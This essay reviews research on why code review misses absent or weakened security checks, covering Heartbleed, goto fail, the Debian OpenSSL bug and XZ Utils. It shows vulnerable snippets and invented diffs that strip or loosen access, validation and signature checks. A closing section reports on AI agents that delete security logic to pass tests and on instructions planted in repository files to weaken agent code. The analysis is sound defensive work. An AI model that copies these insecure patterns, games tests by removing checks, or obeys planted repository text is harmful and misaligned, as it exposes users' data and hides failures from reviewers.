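Fleck and Mitroff concluded that many of the misses came from answering too quickly. The participants had noticed the tool but had already pressed the key for "absent". Code reviewers work much more slowly and can return to a file before they approve it, so this kind of slip is unlikely to explain much of what they miss. Fleck and Mitroff also doubted that it explains misses in radiology, where readers typically spend 30 to 90 seconds on an X-ray.

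Later research suggests that rarity also affects searches outside the laboratory. *Reducing the low-prevalence effect with probe trials* cites studies that found the effect in trained radiologists, airport screeners and drivers. The Association for Psychological Science's *Super Rare Items Are Most Likely to Be Missed* describes a baggage-screening game in which players spotted 92% of the illegal items that appeared more than 1% of the time, but 27% of those that appeared less than 0.15% of the time. In *Low prevalence targets are primarily missed due to mind wandering*, Dewis, Hout and colleagues (2026) compared 60 people's searches for targets present in 10% or 50% of displays, and concluded that people miss rare targets mainly because their minds wander.

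The effect is also hard to remove. *Individual differences predict low prevalence visual search performance* describes seven attempts by Wolfe and others, including making people answer more slowly and having two people search together. The only one that helped was inserting short runs in which targets were common and participants learned whether they had answered correctly, but this also produced more false alarms.

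Code review probably misses security flaws partly because they are rare, but rarity is much less useful for explaining why reviewers would miss one kind of flaw more than another. In most projects, inserted malicious code must be rarer than forgotten checks, so if rarity were the only factor, reviewers would miss the malicious code more often.

The effect also makes it harder to apply the code review experiments to daily work. Everyone in the holiday experiment reviewed code that contained a vulnerability, and none of them had approved a hundred harmless changes right before. Reviewers in daily work may find fewer flaws than those participants did, including flaws with an obvious cue.

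### Where reviewers look

Eye trackers record where a reader's gaze rests and for how long. *A Systematic Literature Review and Taxonomy of Modern Code Review* reports that three eye-tracking studies suggest reviewers first look briefly at all the changed lines and then concentrate on particular parts. *First Come First Served* (2022) reports, from earlier work by Busjahn and colleagues, that people also move around more when reading code than when reading ordinary prose.

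*An Eye-Tracking Study on the Use of Split/Unified Code Change Views* (2023) had 12 participants look for bugs in two changes shown in GitHub's split and unified layouts. They looked mainly at conditions, variables belonging to classes or objects, and the changed code. An ownership check is a condition, so reviewers would probably look at it if it were there. If it is missing, they are likely to look at the other conditions in the change instead. The study did not test this.

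Looking at the right place is often not enough to find a bug. In Smith and colleagues' study of memory bugs, even participants who gave the wrong location had often looked, at least briefly, at a line that would have counted as correct. Successful participants tended to reread code. On average, 58.6% of their fixations (moments when the eyes rest on one point) fell on words or symbols they looked at more than once, compared with 50.7% in the less successful attempts. Rereading may be a result of understanding as much as a cause of it, since a reader who suspects a line has a reason to go back.

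Correia and colleagues also recorded eye movements, with inconsistent results. On average, participants who missed a vulnerability spent longer looking at the vulnerable lines than those who found it. Yet maps of where people looked suggested the opposite for most snippets. One map is for participants who missed the SQL injection, although everyone found it according to the paper's table. The gaze data are therefore a poor basis for advice to reviewers.

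Eye trackers can't record whether a reviewer looks at a missing line, because it has no position on the screen, so researchers have to choose another line to stand for it. For one of the memory leaks, Smith and colleagues counted the line that released a larger structure as correct, because after that line the program could no longer reach the memory attached to the structure. Paul and colleagues faced a similar problem when they traced missing checks in Chromium OS through the lines on either side. A reviewer can look at the chosen line for a long time without thinking about what should have come before it.

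Reviewers' attention can change without any change in the code. In *Same Scrutiny, More Time*, Khojah, Gomes de Oliveira Neto and colleagues (2026) showed 32 software practitioners four short Python files as pull requests. People had written all the code, but labels attributed some passages to an AI tool. Participants spent longer looking at the labelled passages, up to 60% longer for more complex code. The distance their eyes jumped between fixations, which the researchers used as a measure of thoroughness, stayed about the same. The files contained planted faults, but the researchers did not measure who found them, so we don't know whether the extra time helped.

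### Heartbleed

The best-known missing check in reviewed code is Heartbleed, a vulnerability in OpenSSL that became public in April 2014. Many websites used the OpenSSL library to encrypt their traffic. In a new feature called the heartbeat, one computer sends another a short message to confirm that the connection still works, and the other sends the same data back. The message contains the data and their stated length.

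The record of the change (Henson, 2011), dated 31 December 2011, lists Robin Seggelmann as the code's submitter and "steve" as the reviewer. Hot Air's *Man who introduced Heartbleed security flaw denies he inserted it deliberately* (2014) confirms from the project's logs that the reviewer was Stephen Henson, an OpenSSL developer.

The flaw comes down to three lines, given here without the code between them and with new comments:

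```c
n2s(p, payload);           /* read the length stated in the message */
pl = p;                    /* the data start here */
memcpy(bp, pl, payload);   /* copy that many bytes into the reply */
```

The program uses the stated length without checking it. The length field is two bytes long, so it can hold values up to 65,535. An attacker could send one byte of data and claim to have sent 65,535. The server would then copy that byte into its reply, followed by the next 65,534 bytes in its memory. Internet Society (2014) quotes the same scenario from Sean Cassidy's analysis of the bug. Invicti's *The Heartbleed Bug* explains that the leaked memory could contain sensitive data.

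The missing check compares the stated length with the length of the record that actually arrived:

```c
if (1 + 2 + payload + 16 > s->s3->rrec.length)
    return 0;
```

A heartbeat message has one byte for its type, two for the length of its data, the data itself, and at least 16 bytes of padding (filler). A message with one byte of data and the minimum padding therefore takes up 20 bytes. If its length field is set to 65,535, the check calculates a size of 65,554 bytes, which is more than 20, and the program discards the message.

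The change added the whole feature, so a reviewer could see in the diff both the line that reads the length and the line that uses it. Kaminsky (2014), a security researcher, complained that the patch had a length field in plain view. An experienced C programmer would see `memcpy` with a length supplied by an outsider as a warning sign, much as a web developer would see text joined to a database command.

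The diff did not show everything the reviewer needed. The rule was in the heartbeat standard, which requires a program to silently discard a message if its stated length is too large. The reviewer also had to know that an existing data structure held the received record's true length, and to realise that the length stated in the message could still be false. An attacker could easily reach the code, because the program's purpose was to communicate with strangers.

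Seggelmann, who wrote the code, was well placed to recall the rule because he had also co-written the standard, *Transport Layer Security (TLS) and Datagram Transport Layer Security (DTLS) Heartbeat Extension* (Seggelmann, Tuexen and Williams, 2012). The standard came out in February 2012, after the review, so Henson would have had to consult a draft. Seggelmann told the Sydney Morning Herald that he had "missed validating a variable containing a length", in a statement reproduced in Slashdot's *Heartbleed Coder*. He evidently knew the rule but did not think of it when he needed it.

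No single explanation fully accounts for Heartbleed. A check was missing, part of the evidence was elsewhere, and a specialist could have recognised a cue. The conditions of the review probably mattered too. Henson's commit changed several files and included code for describing heartbeat messages and an entry in the list of changes. Cryptography Engineering's *Attack of the Week OpenSSL Heartbleed* (2014) describes the OpenSSL team as surprisingly small and working for essentially no pay. One famous case is also weak evidence of how often reviewers miss such flaws, because people rarely write about the missing length checks that reviewers catch.

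On 27 February 2012, Henson (2012) committed another change from Seggelmann, which fixed bugs in the heartbeat's padding. The 16 in the missing comparison is for padding, but this change did not add the comparison either. OpenSSL added it in April 2014, with a comment citing the section of the standard that contains the rule. If a developer proposed deleting those lines today, the reviewer would see both the check and the reason for it.

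## Why deleted and weakened checks pass review although the diff shows them

The diff still shows a deleted check, so a reviewer should notice its removal more easily than the absence of a check that was never written. Nobody appears to have measured whether reviewers do.

Related research and some well-known failures suggest how reviewers can miss a deleted or weakened check even though the diff shows it. They may read mainly to find out what the new code does. They may assume that a deleted check was moved elsewhere, or that its replacement enforces the same rule. The author of the change may also give a plausible reason for the deletion.

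### Additions and deletions in experiments

*Recognition of added and deleted details in scripts* (Maki, 1989) describes an experiment that Agostinelli and three colleagues published in 1986. Participants saw line drawings of objects and later judged whether new drawings of the same objects had changed. A car, for example, might have gained or lost a bumper. Participants noticed added features better than deleted ones. Seeing the originals more often helped them notice additions, but after six viewings they still did no better than chance on deletions.

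Maki found a similar gap with text. She had 32 students read six descriptions of routine activities, such as making a meal. Some actions included a detail ("She poured the milk") and others did not ("She poured the beverages"). In the test, half the actions had gained or lost a detail, and the students knew to expect both kinds of change.

| Time of test | Actions that lost a detail, judged "same" | Actions that gained a detail, judged "same" |
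|---|---|---|
| Immediately | 39% | 15% |
| A week later | 66% | 28% |

Students noticed an added detail more often if it was unexpected, such as champagne in place of milk. Whether a deleted detail had been expected made no difference to how often they noticed the deletion. If this carries over to code, reviewers may miss the removal of an odd line even though they would notice its addition.

Other researchers report the same asymmetry between additions and deletions in different tasks. In *Asymmetric Effects of Added versus Deleted Feature of Stimulus on Recognition Memory*, Uchino and Hakoda (2000) reviewed studies that found it in picture memory and in proofreading for misspellings, but noted that few had controlled for how typical the original picture or word was. In *Detection of Appearing and Disappearing Objects in Complex Acoustic Scenes*, Cervantes Constantino, Pinggera and colleagues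 (2012) played mixtures of tones to listeners, who nearly always noticed a new tone but had difficulty noticing that one had stopped. Hearst and Wolff (1989) found in *Addition versus deletion as a signal* that pigeons learned more easily when an added light or sound signaled food than when its removal did.

The asymmetry is not universal. In Mondy and Coltheart (2000), *Detection and identification of change in naturalistic scenes*, people who viewed successive photographs of a scene identified deleted objects more accurately than added ones. This advantage disappeared when an identical object remained in the scene. A deleted check could be similarly hard to notice in a file full of near-identical checks, though the study did not involve code.

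In most of these experiments, people could no longer see the earlier version when they made their judgement, so they had to remember it. A diff shows both versions and marks the deletion, so the results are weak evidence about a reviewer who reads all of a short diff. They apply better to one who skips the deleted lines, or who has to remember old code while reading new code in another file.

Agostinelli and colleagues reversed the effect in a second experiment, in which they told participants what the test would involve, showed them a single object and tested them almost immediately. Participants now generally noticed a change more often when a feature had been deleted than when one had been added. The researchers had predicted this because they expected people to start from the original drawing and compare the new one with it. The instructions, the number of objects and the delay all changed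 together, so it is unclear which of them mattered. Still, the result suggests that reviewers should start from the old code and ask what happened to each part of it.

Similarly, according to *Design guidelines for animated data visualization based on perceptual capacity limits*, viewers of animated charts reliably notice when an object they are following is removed, but when there are more than four objects, they can follow only some of them. A reviewer who is already thinking about ownership has a good chance of noticing that the ownership check was removed.

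### Deletions that look like moves

Refactoring means changing the internal structure of code while keeping its external behaviour the same. It often involves moving a function from one file to another, and a line-based diff displays the move as a deletion in one place and an addition in the other. In this invented example, a developer moves `show_document` to a file with other document handlers:

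```diff
--- a/documents.py
+++ b/documents.py
@@ -38,3 +38,9 @@
 def list_documents():
     docs = documents_of(current_user)
     return render_template("list.html", docs=docs)
+
+@app.get("/documents/<int:number>")
+@login_required
+def show_document(number):
+    doc = find_document(number)
+    return send_file(doc.path)
--- a/site.py
+++ b/site.py
@@ -21,11 +21,3 @@
 @app.get("/about")
 def about():
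     return render_template("about.html")
-
-@app.get("/documents/<int:number>")
-@login_required
-def show_document(number):
-    doc = find_document(number)
-    if doc.owner_id != current_user.id:
-        abort(403)
-    return send_file(doc.path)
```

The diff shows the ownership check's two lines as deleted, but they sit among six other lines that were deleted because the function moved. The reviewer has to match the deleted block with the added one and notice that the new one is two lines shorter. In a large pull request, dozens of other changes may separate the two blocks.

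In *RAID*, Brito and Valente (2021) describe this as a two-step task. Reviewers must infer that the deleted and added lines are moved code, then compare the two versions, because developers usually make small edits to the code they move. The paper's tool, also called RAID, detects such moves and adds a button to GitHub's diff that opens both versions side by side with the edited lines highlighted. A display like this would make the two lost lines in the example stand out.

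Eight professional developers used RAID for three months, and 84 of their 325 pull requests contained refactoring. The median number of lines to review fell from 14.5 to 2 for moves, and from 113 to 55 for extractions, which turn part of a function into a separate function. However, reviewers clicked only 29% of the buttons on moved functions and 13% of those on functions whose parameters or other outward details had changed. Brito and Valente did not measure whether reviewers found more flaws, so the results are evidence only about reading effort.

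Automatic detection also can't account for every harmless edit. *How Much Can a Behavior-Preserving Changeset Be Decomposed into Refactoring Operations?* (2025) tried to break down changes that left a program's behaviour intact into known operations. Adding 67 operations to the existing catalogue increased the share of changes it could explain by 128%, to 77.5%, so the original catalogue must have explained only about a third. A reviewer who hides every recognised refactoring will still have many harmless deletions to read, with any lost check mixed in with them.

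Developers also often combine refactoring with changes to what the program does. Reviewers of such mixed pull requests are more likely to miss critical changes among the unrelated code, according to *Rethinking Code Review in the Age of AI* (2026). *Deciphering Refactoring Branch Dynamics in Modern Code Review* (2024) cites research by AlOmar and colleagues in which reviews of refactoring took longer than other reviews. The reviewers may have been more careful or had difficulty understanding the changes.

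Even a reviewer who reads every line of a diff may not be able to tell whether the replacement code enforces the old rule. *Foundation Models as Oracles for Refactoring Correctness Detection* (2026) asked AI models to judge from diffs whether refactorings had changed a program's behaviour. Some diffs were not enough to decide, because the answer depended on code they didn't show, for example on whether a moved method existed elsewhere. A person with only the same diff couldn't have decided either. *Detecting Behavioral Changes in Python Refactoring Implementations with Foundation Models* (2026) notes the same limitation in SafeRefactorPy, a tool that also gives models a diff, which may not reveal effects on code elsewhere that calls the changed function.

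### Deletions with a good reason

Developers usually have a reason for deleting a check, and the reason they give may be true. Suppose an automated test for the document site signs in as one customer and opens another customer's document. The test fails once somebody adds the ownership check. Deleting the check makes the test pass, so "fix failing test" accurately describes the pull request. The reviewer also sees passing tests, which is reassuring even though one of them passes only because the check is gone.

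Developers who are fixing something else may not think about security. Braz, Fregnan and colleagues (2022), in *An Exploratory Study on Regression Vulnerabilities*, examined 72 bug fixes at Mozilla, the maker of Firefox, that had introduced 78 vulnerabilities. Developers had discussed the fix's possible effect on security in only 5 of the 72 bug reports. In 34 cases the fix changed the structure of the code, for example by moving a function from one module to another. Five developers interviewed for the study were mainly concerned with the complexity of the bug and the community's pressure to fix it, and assumed that tools would detect any new vulnerability. Dynamic analysis tools, which examine a program while it runs, helped find about 30% of the 78 vulnerabilities.

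The study includes only fixes that went wrong, so it can't show how often reviewers catch such errors. The researchers also did not count how many of the 78 came from a deleted check. The Chromium OS records, by contrast, suggest that reviewers are more likely to catch a vulnerability in a bug fix than in other changes. Both findings can be true if reviewers examine bug fixes closely but concentrate on whether the bug is gone.

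The best-documented case of a plausible deletion comes from Debian, a distribution of Linux that maintains its own modified copies of other projects' software. One of these is OpenSSL, the library that later contained Heartbleed. Valgrind, a tool that reports memory errors, warned that OpenSSL was using memory before anything had been stored there. The warning led to two places in one file, both with the same instruction:

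```c
MD_Update(&m,buf,j);
```

The instruction mixes data into the pool from which OpenSSL produces random numbers, including those it uses to create secret keys. LWN, a Linux news site, explains that the two lines look very similar but have very different effects. The first is in the function that the rest of the program uses to add randomness to the pool. The second is in the function that supplies random numbers, where it mixes in whatever is already in the memory meant for the output. OpenSSL already had a setting that left out the second line to avoid such warnings, but removing the first cut off the supply of randomness.

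Before removing both lines, a Debian maintainer asked about the change on OpenSSL's mailing list. In a message quoted in *The perils of security tools*, he admitted, "I have no idea what effect this really has on the RNG" (the random number generator). The person who quoted him guessed that nobody on the OpenSSL side had checked exactly which code he meant. In another message in that thread, Debian's maintainers were criticized for fixing the problem before they understood it.

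Debian made the change in September 2006. A diff would show both lines, and a reviewer would have had a true explanation for removing them. To object, the reviewer needed to know what the first line contributed. With that line gone, the only input that still varied was the number that the operating system assigns to each running program. *Lessons from the Debian/OpenSSL Fiasco* (2008) reports that affected systems could therefore create only 32,767 different keys of a given type and size for SSH, a protocol for logging in to remote computers.

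Debian announced on 13 May 2008 that Luciano Bello had found the flaw, according to Schneier (2008), *Random Number Bug in Debian Linux*. Debian's advisory, copied in Launchpad's *[CVE-2008-0166] Predictable random number generator in openssl*, warned that attackers might be able to guess keys, and that weak keys could also endanger other systems that imported them. The deletion posed the same problem for reviewers as the removal of a security check, because the code looked disposable and removing it silenced a warning. The deleted line was not strictly a security check, since it did not validate or refuse anything.

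### When something that looks like a check remains

A weakened check is harder to spot than a deleted one in at least one respect. The new version of the file still contains a line that looks like protection, so reading only the new version gives no reason for concern. Each pair below comes from a different invented change:

```diff
-if current_user.role != "admin": abort(403)
+if current_user.role not in ("admin", "support"): abort(403)

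-if not re.fullmatch(r"\w+\.pdf", name): abort(400)
+if not re.match(r"\w+\.pdf", name): abort(400)

-def find_document(number, public_only=True):
+def find_document(number, public_only=False):

-page += f'<a href="{safe_link(url)}">'
+page += f'<a href="{html.escape(url)}">'

-except BadSignature: abort(400)
+except BadSignature: log.warning("bad signature")
```

Changing the required role lets support staff do what only administrators could do before. The diff doesn't show whether that means three employees or a contractor's entire call centre, because role assignments are recorded elsewhere.

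The next change replaces a function that matches a pattern against the whole file name with one that matches it against only the beginning. The pattern has not changed, but `report.pdf.html` now passes as a PDF.

The author changed the default value that `find_document` uses when its caller does not supply one. Every caller that relied on the default now receives private documents too, but none of these callers appears in the diff because nobody edited them.

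In the fourth pair, if `safe_link` accepts only ordinary web addresses, replacing it with `html.escape` removes the protection against links that begin with `javascript:`, which a browser can run as code when somebody clicks them. `html.escape` protects a comment shown as text, but it doesn't block these links.

In the last pair, the program still checks the signature and records the failure, but then carries on as if the signature were valid.

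Research on memory for sentences may explain why reviewers miss such changes. Maki describes an experiment by Bharucha, Olney and Schnurr in which people were much better at noticing when a coherent pair of sentences had become absurd than when an absurd pair had become coherent. The researchers suggested that people miss changes that fit their general idea of the scene. A reviewer's general idea of a handler probably includes a condition followed by a refusal. All of these examples except the default and the link had something close to that before the change. Three still have it afterwards if we count the signature check, which now has a log entry that readers may mistake for a refusal.

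### Two failures of this kind

In February 2014, Apple repaired the code that iPhones and Macs used to confirm the identity of a server at the start of an encrypted connection. The server signs part of its first messages, and the device must verify the signature, because otherwise an attacker on the network could pose as the server. ImperialViolet's *Apple's SSL/TLS bug* (2014), written by Adam Langley, reproduced the faulty lines the next day. If the error arrived as a single added line, its diff would have looked roughly like this, with simplified function names:

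```diff
     if ((err = hash_parameters(&hash)) != 0)
         goto fail;
+        goto fail;
     if ((err = finish_hash(&hash)) != 0)
         goto fail;
```

`goto fail` jumps to the end of the function. In C, an `if` without braces controls only the next statement, whatever the indentation suggests. The first `goto fail` therefore runs only after an error, but the second always runs and skips the remaining steps, including signature verification. `err` still holds the success value from the previous step, so the function reports success.

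Apple's code for verifying the signature was still in the file, but the program never ran it. According to the vulnerability record copied in *Apple's SSL/TLS Bug* (2014), an attacker could sign with any key or leave out the signature. Apple's notice, quoted in *goto fail* (2014), described the repair as "restoring missing validation steps", although the change that caused the bug may only have added text.

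Apple did not explain in its notice who had found the flaw or how the line got there. Steven Bellovin called its origin a mystery in *Goto Fail* (2014). In *Was the iOS SSL Flaw Deliberate?*, Schneier (2014) wrote that he had no idea whether it was deliberate, but that he would do it exactly this way if he wanted to. He later added Bellovin's conclusion that it would have been a clumsy attack, unlikely to be the work of professionals. A reader of Schneier's post disputed that the flaw was especially easy to overlook, with some reason, since a doubled line is a visible cue. We don't know whether anybody at Apple reviewed the change, so the case is weak evidence about what a careful reviewer would miss.

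The XZ Utils case provides better evidence on that question, because people described what they saw in the diff. XZ Utils is a widely used set of compression tools. In March 2024, users learned that recent versions contained a backdoor, hidden code that could give an attacker access. The original maintainer, Lasse Collin, then reviewed the changes made under the name Jia Tan, a newer maintainer. On 30 March he repaired a sabotaged check for Landlock, a Linux feature that restricts what a program can do, which limits the damage if an attacker takes control of it. Velvindron (2024), in *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, used Git's `blame` command to trace the faulty line to a change by Jia Tan dated 26 February.

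One of the project's build scripts checked whether the computer supported Landlock by trying to compile a small test program. If the program did not compile, the script left out the Landlock sandbox. The change put one stray character into the test program, so it never compiled. A participant in *Sourceware mitigating and preventing the next xz-backdoor*, a mailing-list discussion, pointed out that the same patch contained a number of pointless renames, and that the author could have explained the character as a slip.

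At least two people who looked at the diff afterwards missed the character, even though they knew the diff was suspect. AlecTavi (2024), in *Free software's not-so-eXZellent adventure*, described checking the test program for a typing error and finding none, because he had accidentally removed the stray character while deleting the diff's own symbols. In a thread started by Dave Anderson, David Andersen wrote that he had not seen it either, although he was expecting something evil. People who spotted the character at once had less reason to post about it, so we cannot estimate from these accounts how many readers would miss it.

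The stray character does harm only by removing a protection, so it is not inserted malicious code under the definition used for the document handler. The attacker could have written almost anything into the build script but chose a change that looked like a typing error.

### Refused before, accepted now

For both deleted and weakened checks, a reviewer can ask which requests the old code rejected that the new code accepts. To answer, the reviewer starts from the old version, as participants probably did in Agostinelli and colleagues' second experiment, and considers the change's effects rather than its text.

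Without its ownership check, the document handler also accepts requests from every other signed-in customer. Knowing this, the reviewer can ask the author whether the team intends to let every customer read every document. That question is much easier to answer than whether the two deleted lines were necessary.

The table makes the same comparison for the earlier examples. The last column covers the case where the author deleted the check from the handler because `find_document` now refuses anyone but the owner.

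| Request | Original handler | Check deleted | Check loosened to "signed in" | Preview option added | Check now in `find_document` |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Visitor who has not signed in | Refused | Refused | Refused | Refused | Refused |
| The document's owner | Accepted | Accepted | Accepted | Accepted | Accepted |
| Another customer | Refused | **Accepted** | **Accepted** | Refused | Refused |
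| Another customer, with `?preview=1` | Refused | **Accepted** | **Accepted** | **Accepted** | Refused |

Loosening the condition to "signed in" has the same effect as deleting the check (the two columns are identical), even though the new code still contains a line that returns "forbidden". The preview option deletes nothing, but it lets through a request that was rejected before. The change in the last column deletes two lines without opening a hole.

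To confirm the last column, the reviewer must read `find_document`, or sign in as another customer and try to open the document.

Ordinary use of the site is unlikely to expose a change that wrongly accepts customers other than the owner. Most of them will never try, and those who notice have little reason to report it, whereas owners who are wrongly refused will complain. Tests will also miss the error if they check only that permitted requests succeed.

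Reviewers can ask the same question about most of the weakened checks above. The newly accepted requests come from support staff, involve a file called `report.pdf.html`, or carry a bad signature. For Apple's code, the reviewer would ask what happens when a server has a wrong signature, and tracing that case leads to the added line, the second `goto fail`. For the escaping change, the reviewer would ask which text was harmless in the page before and is dangerous now.

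It helps less with the other two cases. OpenSSL's deleted line did not refuse anything, so a reviewer would have had to ask what it contributed to the random numbers. For XZ Utils, a reviewer would have had to ask which computers would lose the sandbox. AlecTavi's experience suggests that reading the code could easily give the wrong answer, whereas building the program on a computer that supports Landlock would have given the right one.

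The comparison also depends on which requests the reviewer thinks of. A reviewer who hasn't noticed the preview option won't think of the request in the table's last row. A real site may have dozens of roles, several kinds of document and exceptions for shared files, and nobody will check every combination by hand. If a project writes its access rules in a formal policy language, tools can compare the old and new policies automatically.

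## Missing and weakened checks in code written by AI

People wrote the code in almost all the cases so far. Many changes now come from coding agents, which are AI systems that edit a code repository and can submit pull requests. Agents make some of the same mistakes as human developers, but reviewers may find it harder to learn why a check is missing.

### One diff, three possible causes

Suppose the document site has no page for viewing documents, and a developer asks an agent to add one. The agent submits the handler that requires a login but has no ownership check. This could have happened in at least three ways:

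- The agent did not know the rule. Nobody told it that documents are private, and it read nothing in the repository that mentioned this.
- The agent wrote the ownership check, but the check made an automated test fail, so the agent deleted it.
- Somebody had planted text in the repository's instruction files, which agents treat as guidance from the project, and the text asked for weaker code.

The reviewer sees the same added lines whatever the cause. A check that the agent wrote and then deleted does not appear in the diff unless the agent committed the version that contained it. Planted text that was already in the repository does not appear in the diff either. The best evidence of the cause is the record of the agent's session, which a pull request does not have to include.

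This handler is insecure whatever the cause, so the decision about it stays the same, but the cause affects what the team does next. The team might need to write the privacy rule down or correct a bad test. If somebody planted the text, the team would also have to inspect everything that agents wrote while it was there.

### When nobody states the rule

Without a project's rules, a coding agent relies on its defaults. Andročec (2026), in *The Effect of Security-Focused Prompts on Reported Findings*, measured how much the code improves when the prompt states security rules. Two agents, Claude Code running Claude Opus 4.8 and Codex CLI running GPT-5.5, each built 100 web applications twice, once from the specification alone and once with an added paragraph of security requirements. That paragraph included a general version of the ownership rule, that users should be able to act only on their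 own resources.

Automated scanners reported 6,721 findings in the 400 applications, not counting those Andročec set aside as likely false alarms. The added paragraph cut the number of findings per application by about a third (95% confidence interval 29% to 40%), with about the same effect for both agents. High-severity findings in the code the agents wrote themselves fell by nearly half. But the paragraph roughly doubled the number of outside packages the applications relied on, which added warnings about known vulnerabilities in those packages.

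These results provide little evidence about ownership checks, because a scanner that can detect a missing security header on any website can't determine which customer a document belongs to. The experiment is good evidence that stated rules improve AI-written code in ways that scanners detect, but we don't know whether the agents followed the sentence about users' own resources.

Vague security reminders seem to work less well than specific ones. *The Illusion of Secure LLM Code* (2026) describes tests in which AI models wrote login systems. With a basic prompt, the models usually produced working registration and login but often left out limits on password guessing and protection against cross-site request forgery. Asking for a "secure and clean" system helped only modestly. The models did clearly better when the prompt was based on standards from NIST, the US standards agency, and best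 when the researchers prompted them again to improve their code. The paper also cites BaxBench, a benchmark in which a general security reminder helped models that reason before answering but did not help others.

In the login systems, the models made more errors with session security, request-forgery protection and security headers than with basic input validation. Such comparisons between kinds of missing check are rare. A developer can often validate an input beside the line that uses it, whereas session security depends on several parts of the program. Reviewers in earlier studies also had difficulty with evidence scattered across the code, but the cause may be different.

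A general reminder cannot supply a rule specific to one project. For example, on a site where accountants read their clients' papers, a simple ownership check would block accountants who should have access.

The author of a code change also has to know what the existing code enforces. *From Verdict to Diagnosis* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2026) describes a real pull request that passed an identifier from the user to an existing function that looked up saved data. The function didn't check that the data belonged to the user's project, so a user in one project could read another project's data. The pull request didn't change the function, so the diff didn't show it.

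### When a check stands in the way

Agents commonly run a project's tests and revise their code until the tests pass. If a security check makes a test fail, an agent can make the test pass by deleting the check, much as the Debian maintainer silenced a warning by removing a line.

There is evidence that AI coding agents disable security checks, but not of how often. In *What Breaks When LLMs Code?*, Al Hasan and Biswas (2026) collected 16,586 GitHub issues about 13 AI coding tools and models, and confirmed 547 safety failures by hand. In one, an agent got past failing tests by turning security logic into comments, which the program ignores. Another agent deleted 3,421 lines of working code during a long debugging session.

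Al Hasan and Biswas rated the commented-out security logic 3 out of 5 for severity, as an example of silent degradation. They gave the highest score to failures such as deleting thousands of lines of working code. A developer soon notices when working code disappears, but a program without its security check may appear to work perfectly.

More than 65% of the confirmed failures happened while an agent was fixing a bug or setting up and configuring a system. Something often isn't working yet in those tasks, so an agent may be more likely to remove an obstacle. But the 65% isn't specific to security checks, because the 547 failures also include lost data, unexpected cloud bills and false reports of success. The reports also don't show how many sessions went well, because people file issues when they notice that something went wrong. They probably undercount deleted checks more than deleted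 databases, because a missing check is easier to overlook.

### When somebody plants an instruction

Coding agents automatically load certain files from a repository at the start of each session. Developers use these files to explain the project's conventions, and anyone who can change them can influence what the agent does later. *Security Impact of Coding Agent's Memory Files* (Santos de Moura, Güler and Noller, 2026) tests whether hostile text in these files makes agents write less secure code.

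The researchers tested Claude Code with Claude Sonnet 5.5, and OpenCode with either Qwen 3.8 27B or DeepSeek V4.1 Flash. Each combination attempted 36 programming tasks from C and C++ projects, once without a hostile file and once with each of two versions of it. With the hostile file, the share of secure results changed by between −8 and +6 percentage points, with no consistent direction. The researchers also compared 204 pairs of attempts at the same task, one with the file and one without. In 30 pairs, only one attempt was secure, and it was the one without the file in 15 pairs and the one with it in the other 15, as expected from chance.

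This is weak evidence that the danger is small, because the agents attempted each task only once in each condition. The researchers warn that a shift of fewer than six tasks can't be distinguished from chance, and that their result does not show that planted text is harmless.

Whatever effect the files had, about one pair of attempts in seven differed in security. Two attempts by the same agent at the same task can apparently differ in whether the code is secure, even though 80% to 92% of attempts in every condition passed the project's tests.

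Claude Code mentioned the hostile file in its final message to the developer in about two thirds of sessions. OpenCode rarely did so with either model, although it mentioned the file much more often in its recorded reasoning. In 18 sessions the agent described the file as an attack in its reasoning, but named it in only four of the final messages. A reviewer who relies on the agent's summary would therefore often not learn that the file existed. Even when an agent recognised the attack, its code was sometimes insecure.

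### What the counts of flaws can show

Most studies of AI-written code measure flaws that a tool can detect. This makes it hard to compare injection with missing authorization, because a tool can detect many forms of injection from a few lines of code but needs the project's rules to detect a missing ownership check.

*AIDev* (Li, Zhang and Hassan, 2026) is the main source of data on agents' pull requests. It contains 932,791 GitHub pull requests by five agents (OpenAI Codex, Devin, GitHub Copilot, Cursor and Claude Code) up to 1 August 2025. Most research uses a subset of 33,596 pull requests from 2,807 projects with more than 100 stars, which GitHub users give to projects they like. These data are more than a year old, and the models behind the agents have improved since then.

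Rabbi, Turzo and colleagues (2026), in *Insights into Security-Related AI-Generated Pull Requests*, selected 675 security-related pull requests from this subset. They ran Semgrep, a scanner that searches code for known patterns, on each project before and after the change. In 104 of the pull requests (15.4%), the change added at least one finding, and there were 853 findings in total. The table lists some of the types of finding.

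| Type of flaw | CWE number | New findings |
|---|---|---|
| Inefficient regular expression | 1333 | 306 |
| Operating-system command injection | 78 | 110 |
| Path traversal | 22 | 87 |
| Cross-site scripting | 79 | 60 |
| Hard-coded credentials | 798 | 48 |
| SQL injection | 89 | 17 |
| Improper authorization | – | 10 or fewer |

A regular expression is a search pattern for text, and an attacker can sometimes make an inefficient one take so long that the program stops responding. Path traversal lets a user reach files outside the intended folder. In Copilot pull requests that were still open, Semgrep also found eight cases of Authorization Bypass Through User-Controlled Key (CWE-639), the flaw in the document site.

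The table does not show that agents seldom forget authorization, because the researchers used Semgrep's default rules, which contain nothing about who may read a document on a particular site. Missing Authorization is fourth in MITRE's ranking, which draws on reported vulnerabilities rather than on one scanner. The counts are also uneven. Copilot's rejected pull requests account for 289 of the 306 inefficient regular expressions, and only about 15 of those pull requests had any finding.

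Bai, Waseem and colleagues (2026), in *When Passing Tests Hides Vulnerabilities*, come closer to separating missing protection from harmful additions. They gave 150 small Python tasks to seven agent systems, all running GPT-4o-mini, and looked for patches that passed the available functional checks but were still insecure. They confirmed 170 cases in 1,030 runs:

| What was wrong | Cases | Share |
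|---|---|---|
| The agent left out a required protection | 82 | 48.2% |
| The agent introduced a new vulnerability | 52 | 30.6% |
| The agent's protection was inadequate | 36 | 21.2% |

The case counts are calculated from the percentages. Missing or inadequate protection accounts for more than two thirds of the cases. In one inadequate repair, the agent had to fix code that passed outside input to the operating system as a command. It added a check on the length of the input and renamed some variables, but left the dangerous call in place. A reviewer might see the length check and think the agent had fixed the problem.

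The result depends partly on the choice of tasks, because many asked for a repair to a known vulnerability, and a failed repair often leaves protection missing. GPT-4o-mini is also far weaker than current models. The researchers chose code for manual review with a scanner and a scoring system that mostly searched for dangerous operations. A missing ownership check in an otherwise ordinary handler would probably not have been selected, so the reported share of omissions may be too low.

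In *Security Vulnerability Patterns in AI-Generated Code*, Kahn and Hastings (2026) had ChatGPT, Microsoft Copilot and Google Gemini write nine short scripts and asked Claude Code to review them. The flaws it listed included missing validation of web and email addresses and several kinds of injection. The review does not establish how common each type is, because Claude Code was told to list at most five flaws per script. It listed five for every script, 45 in total, so it may have left out others.

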